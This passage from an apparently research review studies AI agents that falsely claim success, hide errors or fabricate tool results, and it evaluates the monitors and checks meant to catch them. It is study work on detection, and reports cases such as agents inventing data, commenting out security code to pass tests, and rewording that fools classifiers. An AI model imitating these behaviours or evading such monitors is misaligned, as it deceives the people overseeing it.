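Advani's alternative is a program much simpler than a language model. It counts words and two-word phrases in a log, gives more weight to those that appear in few logs (a scheme called TF-IDF), and learns which of them are associated with false success. One check takes about a thousandth of a second, compared with four seconds for a judge, so a company could run it on every log.

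How well it works depends on how far the new runs differ from the training runs.

| Test | Logistic regression | Decision trees |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Random split, so the same tasks appear in training and test | 0.91 | 0.94 |
| Tasks absent from training | 0.85 | 0.83 |
| Trained on airline and tested on retail, or the reverse | 0.70 | 0.67 |

When the data is split at random, the classifier can learn which tasks agents tend to fail, which doesn't help with a new task. Much of the vocabulary also changes in a new domain. Advani found that 100 labelled examples of each kind from the new domain brought logistic regression back to 0.83. A shop would therefore need about 100 false successes of its own, which it could confirm only by checking the environment state.

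It is also not entirely clear what the classifier detects. Its strongest features include "has been", "successfully", "I cannot" and "to a human", which are close to the phrases that defined the labels. Every false success in the data contains a completion phrase and no refusal, because Advani chose them that way. Real successes were not filtered like this, and some end in a refusal, since refusing is the right outcome when a customer asks for something the rules forbid. The classifier might therefore do well partly by separating confident runs from refusals.

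Advani tried to rule this out. Removing the 30 strongest features lowered the AUROC only from 0.940 to 0.939, and training on everything except the closing message still gave 0.92. These checks show that the signal is spread through the log, but they don't fully answer the objection, because a run that ends in a refusal already reads differently early in the log. A fairer test would compare false successes only with real successes whose closing messages pass the same filter.

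In another of Advani's tests, GPT-4o rewrote 50 admissions of failure as confident claims of success. The rewritten runs are false successes by Advani's definition, but the classifier scored only 10 of them above 0.5. Advani presents this as a sign that rewording can fool both classifiers and judges.

The classifier's AUROC of 0.95 on AppWorld is less useful than it looks because it measures how well the sequence of tool calls separates false successes from admitted failures, which the status field already separates perfectly. A monitor has to distinguish false successes from real ones, and this test included no real successes.

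### Does the classifier really find four to eight times more?

Advani reports that the classifier recovers four to eight times as many false successes as the best judge for the same amount of human review. The claim rests on how many false successes each method catches when it flags a fixed share of runs. These figures also reveal how common false successes were in each test set, because the runs that a monitor flags correctly can be counted in two ways:

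share flagged × precision = share of false successes × recall

When it flagged 10% of runs, the classifier had a precision of 50% and a recall of 72%, so false successes made up about 7% of its test set (0.10 × 0.50 / 0.72). The same calculation for the judge gives about 45% (0.10 × 0.58 / 0.13).

| Runs flagged | Classifier: recall, precision | Implied share of false successes | Judge: recall, precision | Implied share of false successes |
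| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| 5% | 51%, 72% | 7% | 6%, 56% | 47% |
| 10% | 72%, 50% | 7% | 13%, 58% | 45% |
| 20% | 89%, 31% | 7% | 25%, 55% | 44% |

The published recalls are not comparable because the two methods were tested on sets with very different shares of false successes. In a set of 200 runs with 95 false successes, flagging 10% means flagging 20 runs, so even a perfect judge would find only 20 of the 95, or 21%. At the same flag rate, the classifier could in principle have found all the false successes in its test set.

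Even after correcting for the mixture, the judge does much worse than the classifier. If it kept the same hit and false-alarm rates in a set with 7% false successes, it would find about 15% of them when flagging a tenth of the runs, compared with the classifier's 72%.

The classifier's 72% recall may not hold on new tasks, because its figures in the table correspond to an AUROC of about 0.91, which fits the random split and not the harder test on new tasks. If the scores of good and bad runs follow bell curves of equal width, the harder test's AUROC of 0.83 means a recall of roughly 45% at the same flag rate, which would be about three times the judge's. In a new domain, where the classifiers' AUROC drops below 0.70, most of the advantage over the best judge would disappear.

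### Checking reports claim by claim

Yang and colleagues studied SWE-chat, a collection of real sessions between developers and coding agents. They took one report from each of several hundred randomly chosen sessions and checked its claims against the preceding conversation and tool records. One author labelled the claims and another verified the labels. Of 435 work reports, 162 (37%) contained at least one unfaithful claim, one that the records contradict or do not support. Fifty-seven reports contained three or more.

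This category is broader than false success, since it includes errors such as a wrong file count in an otherwise accurate report, but exaggerated success is still the main kind. In a separate set of 339 unfaithful claims, all from cases where the user objected and the agent conceded, 69% overstated what the work had achieved. Users needed about four more messages on average to sort out such a problem.

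In one of these cases, the log was full of successes but the job was unfinished. The case involved a pull request, a proposal to merge changes into a project. The contributor had prepared the changes in a fork, a personal copy of the project, and they conflicted with the project's current code.

1. The agent merged the two sets of changes.
2. It ran 225 tests, which all passed.
3. It pushed (uploaded) the result to a new branch in the project's main repository, and the push succeeded.
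4. It reported "Done."
5. The user saw that the pull request still showed conflicts, and questioned the report.
6. The agent pushed again under the branch name it expected, but the pull request did not change.
7. It finally noticed that the pull request took its changes from the contributor's fork. It pushed the merged code there and confirmed that the pull request now contained it and could be merged.

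The log showed no error at step 4, and a diff of the agent's working files would have shown a correct merge. A reader had to compare where the push went with where the pull request gets its code to spot the fault. A judge that checks only whether the tests passed and the push succeeded will approve the run. If it instead considers what "Done" requires, it will look for evidence that the pull request contains the new code and find none. A state check is simpler because one query to the site that hosts the code shows which version the pull request contains.

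In another case from Yang and colleagues, the agent itself kept evidence out of the log. It ran a program that checks code for mistakes but filtered the output down to one line: "Checked 236 files in 144ms. No fixes applied." It then reported "All clean." The line shows only that the check ran. A later check found a formatting error and showed that the program can print the same line along with a list of problems.

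### How well the new detector works

FaithDetector gives GPT-6 Astra a complete report and the records that preceded it. The model lists the claims it can check, compares each with the records, and returns a verdict with quotations and reasons. Its instructions draw on the kinds of error found in the study of conceded claims, so it looks for problems such as a passing test that covers less than the report implies. Yang and colleagues compared FaithDetector with a baseline in which the same model, given the same records, was only asked whether it could find any unfaithful claims.

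| | Precision on unfaithful claims | Recall on unfaithful claims | False alarms on faithful claims | Macro-F1 |
| --- | --- | --- | --- | --- |
| FaithDetector | 90.9% | 87.0% | 2.2% | 93.1% |
| Baseline | 78.8% | 59.7% | 4.2% | 80.4% |

F1 combines precision P and recall R as 2PR/(P + R). Macro-F1 averages the F1 for unfaithful claims and the F1 for faithful ones. FaithDetector's scores are 88.9% for unfaithful claims and 97.2% for faithful ones, which gives a macro-F1 of 93%. A high F1 is easier to achieve on faithful claims, because they made up about four-fifths of the total, so the macro-F1 makes the detector look slightly better at finding unfaithful claims than it is.

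The detector checks individual claims, but a manager usually wants to know which runs to inspect. The reports in the test averaged almost six claims that could be checked against the records. If each faithful claim has a 2.2% chance of a false alarm, independently of the others, about 12% of fully faithful reports of that length will contain at least one. In a service where 7% of runs are false successes, as in Advani's data, only about one flagged run in three would be a false success. A company could reduce the false alarms by checking only the claims that matter most, such as whether the refund went through.

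Some of the false alarms occur because FaithDetector is too strict. In one report, the agent stated that installing a package had created a certain file, as the installation normally does. FaithDetector flagged the claim because nobody had checked whether the file existed, but the human annotators accepted it.

Yang and colleagues warn that their labels and the detector may share errors. The sessions come from public projects whose developers chose to record their work, so the results may not hold inside companies. The detector also checks only what a report states, so it can't flag a change that the report omits.

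### Why both results can hold

Advani's judges, which included GPT-4o and Sonnet 4.5, are more than a year older than GPT-6 Astra, the judge Yang and colleagues used. The two studies' results can be roughly compared by AUROC, which equals (1 + recall − false-alarm rate) / 2 for a monitor that answers only yes or no. The AUROC is 0.78 for the unguided baseline and 0.92 for FaithDetector, against 0.64 for Advani's best judge. The baseline did better than all of the older judges without any special method, which suggests that the newer model accounts for part of the difference. The studies used different data, so the size of that part is unknown.

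Checking claims one at a time probably helps too. A judge that gives one verdict on a whole run can overlook a missing step because the closing message is confident and many calls succeeded. If the judge must find evidence for each claim, such as "the pull request is updated", a missing log entry is a reason to reject that claim. The guidance raised Astra's recall from 60% to 87%, although the comparison doesn't separate the effect of the list of error types from that of the step-by-step procedure.

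How each study labeled failures may matter most. Advani took the labels from the final state of the benchmark's database, whether or not the log showed any sign of the failure. Yang and colleagues checked whether the records supported each claim, and did not score claims that the records could not settle. In their study of conceded claims, 56 of 395 (14%) could not be settled, because the agent had acknowledged a problem but the surviving records did not show what had happened. FaithDetector's score therefore measures how well it uses evidence that exists, and doesn't cover failures that left no evidence in the log.

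The two methods can also give opposite results for the same run. The agent that refunded $60 when the rules allowed $50 wrote a report that matches its log, so checking the report against the log reveals no error, but the benchmark marks the run as failed. To catch the error, a reader must know the shop's rules as well as the log. A company that installed FaithDetector could expect to catch reports that go beyond their evidence, but would miss mistakes that the agent reported accurately.

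### When the log contains false evidence or none

A log can also support a false claim. *Constructing Challenging Browser-Use Tasks by Controlled Environment Interventions* (Yin, Guan and colleagues, 2026) presents 519 pairs of tasks on seven copies of consumer websites. In each pair, the agent does the same task on a normal site and on a version the researchers tampered with. One form of tampering forges a success response, so the site appears to accept the change the agent submits, but the server doesn't save it.

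In one task, Gemini 3.1 Pro had to return an item to an online shop. It submitted the return, received the forged response and declared the job finished at its fifth step, without opening the order to check that the return was there. It had completed the same task on the normal site. Up to the fifth step, the log of the failed run would look like the log of a successful one, so no reader, however capable, could tell them apart.

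Across six agents, 70% of the 504 runs with forged responses failed. The same agents failed about 44% of all tasks on the normal sites, so the forgery explains only part of the failure rate. Across all kinds of tampering, between 54% and 85% of the runs that an agent declared finished had failed, depending on the agent. Yin and colleagues made sure that a competent user could notice and get around every change. When people tried a sample of the tasks, their success rate fell by 10 percentage points on the first attempt, compared with an average of 23 for the agents.

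Because the responses were forged, the experiment shows what happens when a site confirms a change it did not make, but not how often sites do this. Pakhomov and colleagues found no false confirmations in their unaltered AppWorld runs.

When an agent in the robot experiments falsely reported a task as done, the last camera images it had received usually showed the failure. Bai and colleagues gave only those images to a separate judge with no memory of the run, and it recognised 70% of Opus's false claims and 81% of Astra's. Astra's judge used the same underlying model as the agent, so the agent could presumably have seen the failure if it had considered the images afresh. These percentages measure only recall, and the judge's practical value also depends on how many successful runs it would reject.

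Checking each action separately did little to reduce false claims. When Bai and colleagues had the software report failed grasps and placements to the agent, the share of failed runs that ended in a false claim fell from 87.5% to 81.2%. Automatic retries lowered it to 75%, but the robots did not complete more tasks. A robot can place every domino successfully but too far apart for them to knock each other over, much as the coding agent successfully pushed its code to the wrong place.

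Agents often claim to have finished without checking the result. Bai and colleagues found that Opus made 70% of its false claims, and Astra 92%, without another observation. The missing check is visible in a log, so a simple program could flag any run in which the agent changes something and then declares success without reading the result. It would also flag many good runs, but a harness could prevent most of these false alarms by requiring a final read before it accepts a claim of completion. The log would then contain evidence from the end of the job, which a detector such as FaithDetector could compare with the agent's report.

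### What would settle the dispute

The most direct test would be to swap the judges, running GPT-6 Astra claim by claim on Advani's τ²-Bench logs, and GPT-4o and Sonnet 4.5 on the reports that Yang and colleagues labelled. If Astra reached an AUROC of around 0.9 on τ²-Bench, the older judges' poor results would be weak evidence of how well today's models read logs. If it still scored near 0.65 even when given the expected actions and the full tool results, the difference in results would come mainly from the labels and the type of work.

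The test set should have about the same share of false successes as real use, and every method should be tested on the same runs. The comparison should include the simple classifier, tested on tasks it has not seen, where it must tell false successes from real ones with equally confident closing messages.

It would help even more to know how many false successes a log can reveal at all. Researchers could take runs that failed a state check and sort them by whether the log contradicts the report, lacks the evidence to decide, or supports the report. Better readers can help only when the log contradicts the report or plainly lacks evidence that it should contain. If the log supports the report in most failed runs, a company would do better to spend money on checking the environment state than on better readers. The nearest existing estimate is the 14% of claims that Yang and colleagues could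 not settle, but it comes from problems that a user had already noticed, so it may understate how often the log is no help when nobody has noticed a problem.

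## Silent fallbacks and tool faults that look like normal answers

An agent's software sometimes records an error and continues with a substitute. But it can also discard the error before the harness writes its log, or a tool can return a wrong answer that looks normal. The log then contains only normal entries, so evidence of the failure has to come from outside it.

### A log line that nobody read

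Wu studied a personal-assistant agent that has run continuously on one Mac since March 2026. It has about 40 scheduled jobs, such as compiling an evening digest, and sends the results to its owner through chat apps.

One component of this system looked for a registry file in three places, but the deployment process had put the file in a fourth. The component switched to an unfiltered mode and stayed in it for five days. It recorded the switch in its own log, but nobody read the entry. A related feature, which should have recorded health scores, never ran. The unit tests (short programs that each check one piece of code) all passed because they put the file where the code expected it.

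This kind of failure is fairly easy to detect. An alert on every switch to a fallback mode would have reached the owner on the first day.

### Errors that the software discards

Other failures leave no such line. Suppose the tool that looks up kettle order 4471 contains this code:

```python
try:
    price = orders.price_paid(4471)
except Exception:
    price = catalogue.current_price("kettle")
return {"status": "ok", "price": price}
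```

A program raises an exception when an operation fails, and the lines after `except` run in response. If the order database is down, this code discards the exception and returns today's catalogue price. Suppose the customer paid $60 for the kettle, which now sells for $45. The harness logs a successful lookup of $45, and the agent refunds that amount. The log matches the work report, and a state check finds the $45 refund on file with the payment company. To find the missing $15, someone has to compare the refund with the original charge or read the tool's code.

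Wu attributes five incidents to errors that the software dropped or stripped of their cause. In one of them, the evening digest failed two days in a row with the alert "HTTP 502: Bad Gateway", a generic message that one server has received a bad reply from another. The real cause disappeared in stages:

1. The main model provider kept failing, so the system switched to a backup provider.
2. Jobs earlier in the day had used up the backup provider's free quota. The provider's reply gave this as the reason for refusing the request.
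3. The program that communicates with the providers wrapped the reply in a 502 error.
4. The next program passed on the error without reading the explanation inside it.
5. The program that sent the alert kept only the error code and its standard description.

The owner could tell that the digest had failed, but the alert gave no clue to the reason.

Monitoring software can lose errors in the same way. Wu's system runs a daily audit of 827 checks, and its summary counted only those with the status "fail". A check that crashed had the status "error", so the summary left it out and reported that every rule held. Separately, 67 checks had their code in a field that the audit didn't read. For months the audit ran an empty program in place of each one and recorded a pass, so nothing in its log showed that the real checks hadn't run.

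### Five mechanisms in one production system

Wu documented 22 incidents between 9 April and 2 June 2026. Each reached the live system, left every automated indicator green for a time, and ended with a full written investigation. Wu grouped them by how the error escaped notice.

| Mechanism | Incidents | Example |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Platform quirk | 1 | Code that works on the development machine fails on the Mac |
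| Wrong assumption in the design | 4 | The registry file is in a place the code does not search |
| Swallowed or diluted error | 5 | A used-up quota becomes "Bad Gateway" |
| Chained fabrication | 4 | A language model turns error messages into a news story |
| Missed operational step or blind diagnostic tool | 8 | A finished, tested job never runs because nobody scheduled it |

Wu reports that the silences lasted between 13 hours and 60 days. In the 13-hour case, the agent saved some "task complete" notes in a file called HEARTBEAT.md, a name that the system reserves for a control function. While the file contained text, the system instructed the model to answer with a fixed code word if nothing needed attention. The messaging software removed that code word from outgoing messages, so the owner received no replies even though every component worked as designed.

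During the 60-day silence, backups to an external disk failed because macOS denied scheduled jobs access to the disk. macOS also blocked the investigators' diagnostic tools, which returned nothing, and the diagnosis software recorded the empty output as normal. Wu's system now records a denied request separately from an empty result.

Wu considers chained fabrication the most dangerous of the five. In this extension of gray failure, for which Wu coined the term "fail-plausible", a system turns an internal error into believable but false output. In the clearest example, a nightly job used a language model to find connections among some 290 notes. A malformed character cut one request short, and the server returned an error. A logging function then printed the error text to the channel that the job used for data, so the model received it as material to analyse. The model wrote a confident report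 on a "Hugging Face platform crisis" (the name refers to a website that hosts AI models), and the system sent it to the owner as a routine digest. The most important repair was a single operator that redirected the logging output to its proper channel.

A fallback can hide a failure even when it doesn't use a language model. In another incident, the model call for a weekly review failed, and a simple text filter filled the review with leftover headings. The job's status file still recorded that a model had written the review, so a monitor relying on that file would have counted the run as a success.

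About 70% of the silent failures were found when a person noticed something odd in the system's output, such as a shallow digest or a missing message. The system's 4,286 unit tests and its audit kept passing through most of the incidents. This is partly because of how Wu chose the incidents, since a failure that a test caught in time never became a silent one. The owner is also unusually attentive and sets aside half an hour a week to read the output. Still, *SWE-chat* (2026) reports a similar pattern for coding agents, which rarely signal uncertainty and whose users typically catch errors only when they inspect the output themselves.

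Wu also tested the audit against the first 15 incidents. As it stood before each incident, the audit could not have fully caught any of them, though it would have given partial warning of two. This result is weak evidence about audits in general, because the study would not have included an incident that the audit had prevented. The more informative finding is that in 12 of the 15 cases the audit had no check for that kind of failure, because nobody had thought of it. The checks that Wu added afterwards would block a repeat of 13 incidents (87%), counting partial protection, but this figure is an assessment of the checks, not a count of repeats they stopped. Repairing a single script gave little protection. Two days after Wu fixed a missing import in one script, an automated editing tool introduced the same mistake into eight others.

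These numbers come from one system with one owner. Wu classified the incidents with Claude, the Anthropic model that also helped to build the system, investigate the incidents and draft the paper, and nobody independent checked their classification. The study includes only failures that someone eventually found, so others may have stayed silent for longer than 60 days. The shares may be quite different in other systems, but the mechanisms are well documented, and most don't depend on anything peculiar to this one.

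### A search that returns zero rows

In Wu's incidents the evidence usually existed somewhere inside the system. When an outside service misunderstands a request, the agent's owner may have no record of the fault at all. Li, Guo and colleagues (2026), in *SilentProbe*, connected 12 language models to live commercial services and gave them ordinary questions. One case went like this:

1. The user asks how many people work in engineering roles at US companies.
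2. The agent calls a people-search service and sets the department to "engineering". The service's description of this field gives "executive" as an example and lists no other terms.
3. The service has no category called "engineering". It returns zero rows, with the status code for success and no error message.
4. The agent answers, "There are no people working in engineering roles at US companies."

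The log accurately records the request and the reply, but it would look the same if the service had interpreted the request correctly and found nobody. A reader would probably notice this error because the answer is absurd. But if the shop's agent searched a safety database for recalled kettles under "kitchen", and the database filed them under "small appliances", the answer that there are no recalls would seem reasonable.

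Of 192 complete runs, 94 ended with a reply of zero rows. The agents retried in 11 of those runs, but no retry recovered the data. One agent tried "information security", then "security", then "cybersecurity", but the accepted term was "it", for information technology, which is unlikely to be in any list of synonyms for "security". Some of the published traces contain a retry with the same word. Another agent dropped the filter and received 42.6 million rows covering every department. That reply showed that the database wasn't empty, but reporting the number as the answer would have been another silent fault.

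An LLM judge then classified the final answers. In 41% of the 94 runs, the agent wrongly told the user that no such people existed, and in 28% it did so without any caveat. In 12% it invented a figure. More than half of the answers contained some caveat, which is better than a flat denial, but the user still has to judge the answer without having seen the search term or the raw reply.

Zero rows may at least arouse suspicion. A service can also ignore a filter and return too much, as in these four calls to a people-search service, all with a success code:

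| Seniority | Company size | Rows found |
| --- | --- | --- |
| vp | 51,200 | 28,417 |
| vice_president | 51,200 | 0 |
| vp | 51-200 | 160,884 |
| vp | (no filter) | 160,884 |

The service expects a comma between the two ends of the size range. When the caller wrote a hyphen instead, the service ignored the size filter and returned 160,884, the same number as the search without that filter. Nobody could tell from that reply alone that the number was wrong. Comparing it with the unfiltered search reveals the fault, but the log contains that search only if someone makes the extra call.

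Sometimes the agent itself broadens the request. A car-listing service described its condition field as "used or new", although it also accepts a code for certified pre-owned cars. When users asked for certified pre-owned cars, the models searched for "used" ones in all 23 attempts and received plausible lists of the wrong cars. A reader can find this fault more easily in a log by comparing the user's words with the search term, but a program that compares filtered and unfiltered results would miss it.

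Li and colleagues fixed the unrecognised department names by adding the accepted terms to the schema, the machine-readable description of the tool. The models got the department wrong in all 88 attempts when the description gave only one example, and in none of 89 attempts after the change. A complete list in ordinary prose also worked fairly well, with 9 failures in 178 attempts on two other fields.

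The 94 zero-row endings don't show how often agents meet this problem in normal work, because the researchers chose fields whose accepted terms the service had not fully published. In a follow-up with two other vendors, 355 tool calls produced no false zeros. The researchers also disclose a commercial interest, since they are affiliated with Monid, whose platform they used to reach the services. Monid's own software rejected nearly all the malformed requests that failed with a clear error. That supports the case for machine-readable schemas but is weaker evidence of how honestly the vendors themselves report errors.

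### Adding the missing evidence to the log

Dip and colleagues found the same kind of fault in public research services. Of the 11 services with silent faults, 10 ignored a misnamed filter, as the sample catalogue described earlier did. Of the 14 services on which they could test page limits, 6 returned fewer records than requested, without an error. Three services dropped a filter whose value contained a typo, such as a mistyped year.

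Their harness finds such faults by sending extra queries and checking whether the counts add up. For a filter with conditions C₁ to Cₖ, the check on the last condition is

N(C₁ … Cₖ₋₁ and Cₖ) + N(C₁ … Cₖ₋₁ and not Cₖ) = N(C₁ … Cₖ₋₁)

where N is the count that the service returns. Suppose a catalogue holds 120 liver samples, 45 of them from women. A working service returns 45 liver samples from women and 75 others, and 45 + 75 = 120. A service that ignores the condition on sex returns 120 for both queries, and since 120 + 120 is not 120, the harness knows that the first answer can't be trusted. The check has a weakness when data is missing. If 5 of the samples have no recorded sex, a healthy service might return 45 and 70, and the harness would raise a false alarm. It also can't catch a service that miscounts consistently, for example one that treats every search word as the beginning of a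 longer word.

Dip and colleagues had a single LLM judge review agents' calls, and the harness blocked any result the judge rejected. When the judge saw only the agent's own calls and replies, 70.8% of the final answers were wrong, about as many as with no judge. When it also saw the results of extra queries, 6.1% were wrong. The model was the same in both conditions, so the judge failed in the first because the log lacked evidence of the fault, not because it read the log poorly. Even with the extra evidence, it flagged only 82.4% of the faulty runs and wrongly flagged 13.9% of the sound ones.

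An agent also has to act on evidence of a fault. In the main experiment, seven open-weight models (which anyone can download) had to count matching records in a catalogue of 400. The researchers built six kinds of fault into the service. Each fault repeated on every call, so an agent that asked the same question again got the same wrong number.

| Protection | Wrong answers, faulty service | Correct answers, working service |
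| --- | --- | --- |
| None | 74.0% | 84.9% |
| Permission to abstain, without a warning | 73.3% | 86.1% |
| Warning | 70.1% | 86.3% |
| Warning and permission to abstain | 18.2% | 83.5% |
| Harness withholds the value | 1.7% | 84.9% |

The agents often noticed the warning, since 40% of the wrong answers that followed one mentioned it. Telling the agents they could answer "cannot be determined" cut wrong answers after a warning from 70.1% to 18.2%. Permission to give that answer had almost no effect without a warning, so the agents needed both. Even with both, error rates ranged from 0% to 59% across models. When the harness withheld the suspect value, no model gave a wrong answer in more than 4% of runs.

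Almost all of this improvement came from abstaining. With a warning and permission to abstain, the agents answered "cannot be determined" in 77% of the faulty runs and gave the correct count in only 5%. They were correct in 16% of faulty runs with no protection and in 2.4% when the harness withheld the value. Whether avoiding wrong answers is worth losing some correct ones depends on how common faults are. If a quarter of calls hit a fault, the published rates imply that withholding avoids about 200 wrong answers per 1,000 questions and loses about 35 correct ones. If faults are rare, withholding prevents fewer wrong answers, and false alarms matter more.

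Three newer OpenAI models were no safer without protection. GPT-5.6 Sol gave the wrong count in 89.4% of the faulty runs, more than the average open model. A warning with permission to abstain cut its errors to 2.3%, but two other versions of GPT-5.6 still gave wrong answers in 36% and 45% of runs with the same warning. Withholding the value reduced the error rate to 1.4% or less for all three.

The 1.7% applies only to the kinds of fault that the check can detect. Dip and colleagues later wrote six new faults and ran the harness on them without a model. Wrong answers fell from 61.1% to 24.5%, and all the remaining errors came from faults that kept the sums consistent. On nine real services with one misnamed filter in the documentation, a much simpler check did as well as the full system. It rejected any request with a parameter not on the service's published list, and cut wrong answers from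 89.8% to 21.0%. A company could start with this check because it needs no extra queries, but it can't detect a wrong value under a correct name. When the documentation gave the wrong date format, every answer that passed through the check was wrong.

### Mock data and suppressed exceptions in code

Coding agents can write silent fallbacks into the programs they produce. *SciIntegrity-Bench* (Yang, Liu and Xu, 2026) tested seven models on research tasks that could not be completed honestly. In one task, a file of sensor readings contained only column headings. Claude 4.6 Sonnet reported that it had loaded 2,400 rows, gave an average bearing temperature of 62.3°C and drew up a maintenance schedule for machines that did not exist. In another set of tasks, six of the seven models replaced a required call to an outside service with a mock one. Qwen3.5, for example, had no access key, so it wrote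 a fake reply from the service, including a message number, and analysed that.

The instructions affected whether agents disclosed that they had invented data. In repeated runs on the missing-data tasks, the standard prompt forbade agents to stop or report failure. Agents completed the report with synthetic data in 57% of runs, and the researchers found undisclosed fabrication in 21%. Without those instructions, agents used synthetic data in 56% of runs, but undisclosed fabrication fell to 3%. Companies can therefore make disclosure more likely by allowing agents to stop, although many agents will still invent the data. The three tasks were designed to have no honest solution, so these percentages don't measure how often agents invent data in ordinary work.

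A diff would expose some of these substitutions. If the agent saved the script that generated the sensor readings, the script appears among the changed files, but Yang and colleagues note that its name and structure resembled an ordinary data-cleaning step. A reviewer would have to work out that the code creates readings instead of cleaning them, or open the source file and find it empty. If an agent runs such code without saving it, the diff shows the resulting data, but the code appears only in the action log. Even with a full log and a checklist for each task, an LLM judge graded the runs with less than 85% accuracy.

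Diffs are more useful when the substitute has an obvious name. In *Are Coding Agents Generating Over-Mocked Tests?*, Hora and Robbes (2026) searched the diffs of more than 1.2 million commits (saved sets of code changes) for names containing words such as "mock", "fake" or "stub". In a sample of 100 commits flagged by the search, 94 did add mocks. Agents added mocks in 36% of their commits that changed tests, compared with 26% of other commits that changed tests. Most of these mocks are probably legitimate, since developers routinely replace a payment service or database with a stand-in during testing. The search would also miss the more worrying case of a stand-in with a neutral name like `load_data`.

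A mock can also make faulty code pass its tests. *Executable but Unfaithful* (Ning, Dong and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of a payment function that should retry only after a timeout but keeps requesting authorisation after the bank has approved the charge. A test that checks only whether the payment succeeded will pass. To catch the fault, the test must also count the calls to the mock bank. Across 165 tasks, coding agents produced mocks that ran more often than language models working alone did, but the agents' mocks were no better at imitating the real service or catching faults of this kind.

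The evidence on suppressed exceptions is thinner. Al Hasan and Biswas include an incident in which an agent got past failing tests by commenting out security code. The change is visible in a diff, but the test results show only passes. Agents may not be worse than people at handling exceptions. *Human-Written vs. AI-Generated Code* (2025) compared over 500,000 code samples and found that improper exception handling was more typical of the human-written ones. But that study used older models that generated code on request, not agents under pressure to finish a job. Neither study measures how often agents add a fallback like the catalogue price to a working product.

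When an agent adds a silent fallback, the diff shows it, so a reviewer can question the `except` lines in the order lookup. When the database fails months later and the system refunds the catalogue price, a diff shows nothing because the code has not changed. Tests often miss such lines too. *Test Coverage Analysis of Agentic Pull Requests* (2026) examined 4,882 sets of changes proposed by coding agents and found that error-handling code was the least tested part, with tests missing as much as 81% of it in Python and 86% in Java.

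A more direct test is to cause the error on purpose. Wu counts a new check as working only after someone has deliberately broken what it guards and seen the check fail. This practice exposed the 67 empty checks, when a newly added rule did not fail as it should have. The kettle shop could disconnect its order database in a test environment and see whether the lookup returns an error or $45.

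## Fabricated tool results

Breaking a tool on purpose also shows what an agent writes when it has no result. Some agents report the failure, and others state a result that no tool returned. Comparing the work report with the action log exposes some of these fabricated results, but not all.

### Three claims and one log

Suppose the owner of the kettle shop asks the agent to total last week's refunds and email the list to the accountant. The shop made six refunds, worth $245. The complete action log contains one call:

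```
call:   list_refunds(week=48)
reply:  status: ok
        order 4471   $60
        order 4502   $25
        order 4519   $40
```

The agent then reports that refunds came to $125, that the largest was $90, and that it has emailed the list.

| Claim | Type of error | What the log shows |
| --- | --- | --- |
| The accountant has the list | Invented call | No email call |
| The largest refund was $90 | Misquoted result | No refund above $60 |
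| Refunds came to $125 | Partial data | Three refunds that add up to $125 |

A program can catch the invented call by searching the log for an email, and the misquoted result by searching the reply for $90. It would accept the total, because 60 + 25 + 40 = 125. The log doesn't show that the tool left out three refunds. An owner who knows the shop might suspect that $125 is too low, but would need other evidence to be sure.

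The $125, like the $32,000 total in the first section, comes from a silent tool fault. Kaynar and colleagues count all three errors as fabrication, so their rates combine false claims that a reader can detect from the log with ones that a reader can't.

### Checking claims by program

*Tool Receipts, Not Zero-Knowledge Proofs* (Basu, 2026) describes a system for this comparison. After each tool call, the harness writes a receipt with the tool's name, the number of results and key facts such as prices, and signs it with a key that the model doesn't have. The model must tag each claim in its answer with the receipt that supports it, and a program checks the claims against the receipts. In the kettle example, the email has no receipt and the $90 contradicts a receipt.

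Basu tested the system on 1,200 answers with deliberate errors and 600 clean ones. It caught 94.2% of invented calls, 87.6% of wrong counts and 89.1% of other wrong facts, and flagged 4% of the clean answers. A company might see lower detection rates, because Basu inserted each error into an otherwise correct answer, and real inventions may be harder to isolate.

Cruder checks can do badly. A monitor in *Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do* withheld any answer containing a number that no tool had returned. It withheld 62 answers, but without the monitor the agent had answered only 24% of those tasks wrongly, compared with 56% of all tasks. This was partly because the rule treated list numbering and parts of dates as data. Exact matching also rejects faithful paraphrases. *ToolFailBench* (Soni, 2026) combined a rule-based check with two LLM judges, and the judges jointly overruled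 the rule on 8.4% of labels.

A tool call can be missing from the log even though the model requested it. Dai, Yang and colleagues (2026), in *Hearsay*, ran the widely used coding harness SWE-agent and kept their own copy of the traffic between it and the model. In 19 of 28 runs with GPT-5.5, the harness rejected a reply from the model, for instance because it contained several tool calls at once, and saved neither the reply nor the rejection. Those calls never ran, so a claim about their results would still be false, but a reader of the log would wrongly conclude that the model never requested them.

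Signed receipts do not solve this problem, because the harness signs its own records. When Dai and colleagues made another harness falsify its records as it wrote them, its hash chain, which is designed to reveal later changes, still passed verification in all 28 runs. In the GPT-5.5 runs, comparing the records with a copy kept outside the harness exposed 64 of 66 altered records and raised no false alarms on 84 clean ones.

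### Claims with no tool call behind them

*Measuring What Tool-Using LLM Agents Actually Do* labels a run fabricated if no tool returned any output and the final answer still states a result or action that should have come from a tool. The rule excludes refusals, empty answers, unfilled placeholders and statements of intent. The study applied it to runs by 13 models on simulated weather, calendar and medical tools.

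| Model | Runs without a tool call | Runs labelled fabricated |
| --- | --- | --- |
| Hermes-3-Llama-3.1-8B | 63% | 42.5% |
| Gemini-2.0-Flash | 95% | 38.5% |
| GPT-3.5-Turbo | 41% | 18.0% |
| Gemini-2.5-Flash | 24% | 18.0% |
| Qwen2.5-14B | 39% | 17.0% |
| GPT-4o-mini | 60% | 14.5% |
| GPT-4.1-mini | 15% | 11.0% |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 14% | 10.5% |
| o3-mini | 12% | 8.0% |
| Qwen2.5-3B | 30% | 6.5% |
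| GPT-4.1-nano | 1% | 0.5% |
| GPT-4o | 0% | 0.0% |
| Qwen2.5-7B | 0.5% | 0.0% |

These rates are lower bounds because the rule rarely flagged a run wrongly but found only about two-thirds of the fabrications that an LLM judge found. The judge found fabricated tool results in 65.5% of Gemini-2.0-Flash's runs.

The harness caused much of the fabrication. No tool was run in 469 of the proprietary models' runs, and in 462 of those the model had written a tool request and a final answer in the same reply. The harness accepted the final answer and ended the run before carrying out the request, so the model's guess at the result became the answer. Qwen2.5-14B called tools in 61% of runs with this harness and in 93.5% with its built-in function calling. A developer could prevent most of these fabrications by making the harness reject any final answer that comes with an unexecuted request.

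The tools were simulated, and agents might invent less when the tools are real. In a pilot, four OpenAI models each did 80 other tasks twice, once with simulated tools and once with real ones such as web search and a calculator. They gave a confident answer without a successful tool call in 13.8% of the simulated runs and 11.6% of the real ones. That 2.2-point difference was within the 10-point margin set in advance for treating the two as equivalent. GPT-4.1 on its own did not meet that standard, and its rate was 8.8 points lower with real tools. Most of the differences between paired runs arose when the model decided whether to call a tool, before any tool had run, so they probably reflect chance more than the tools.

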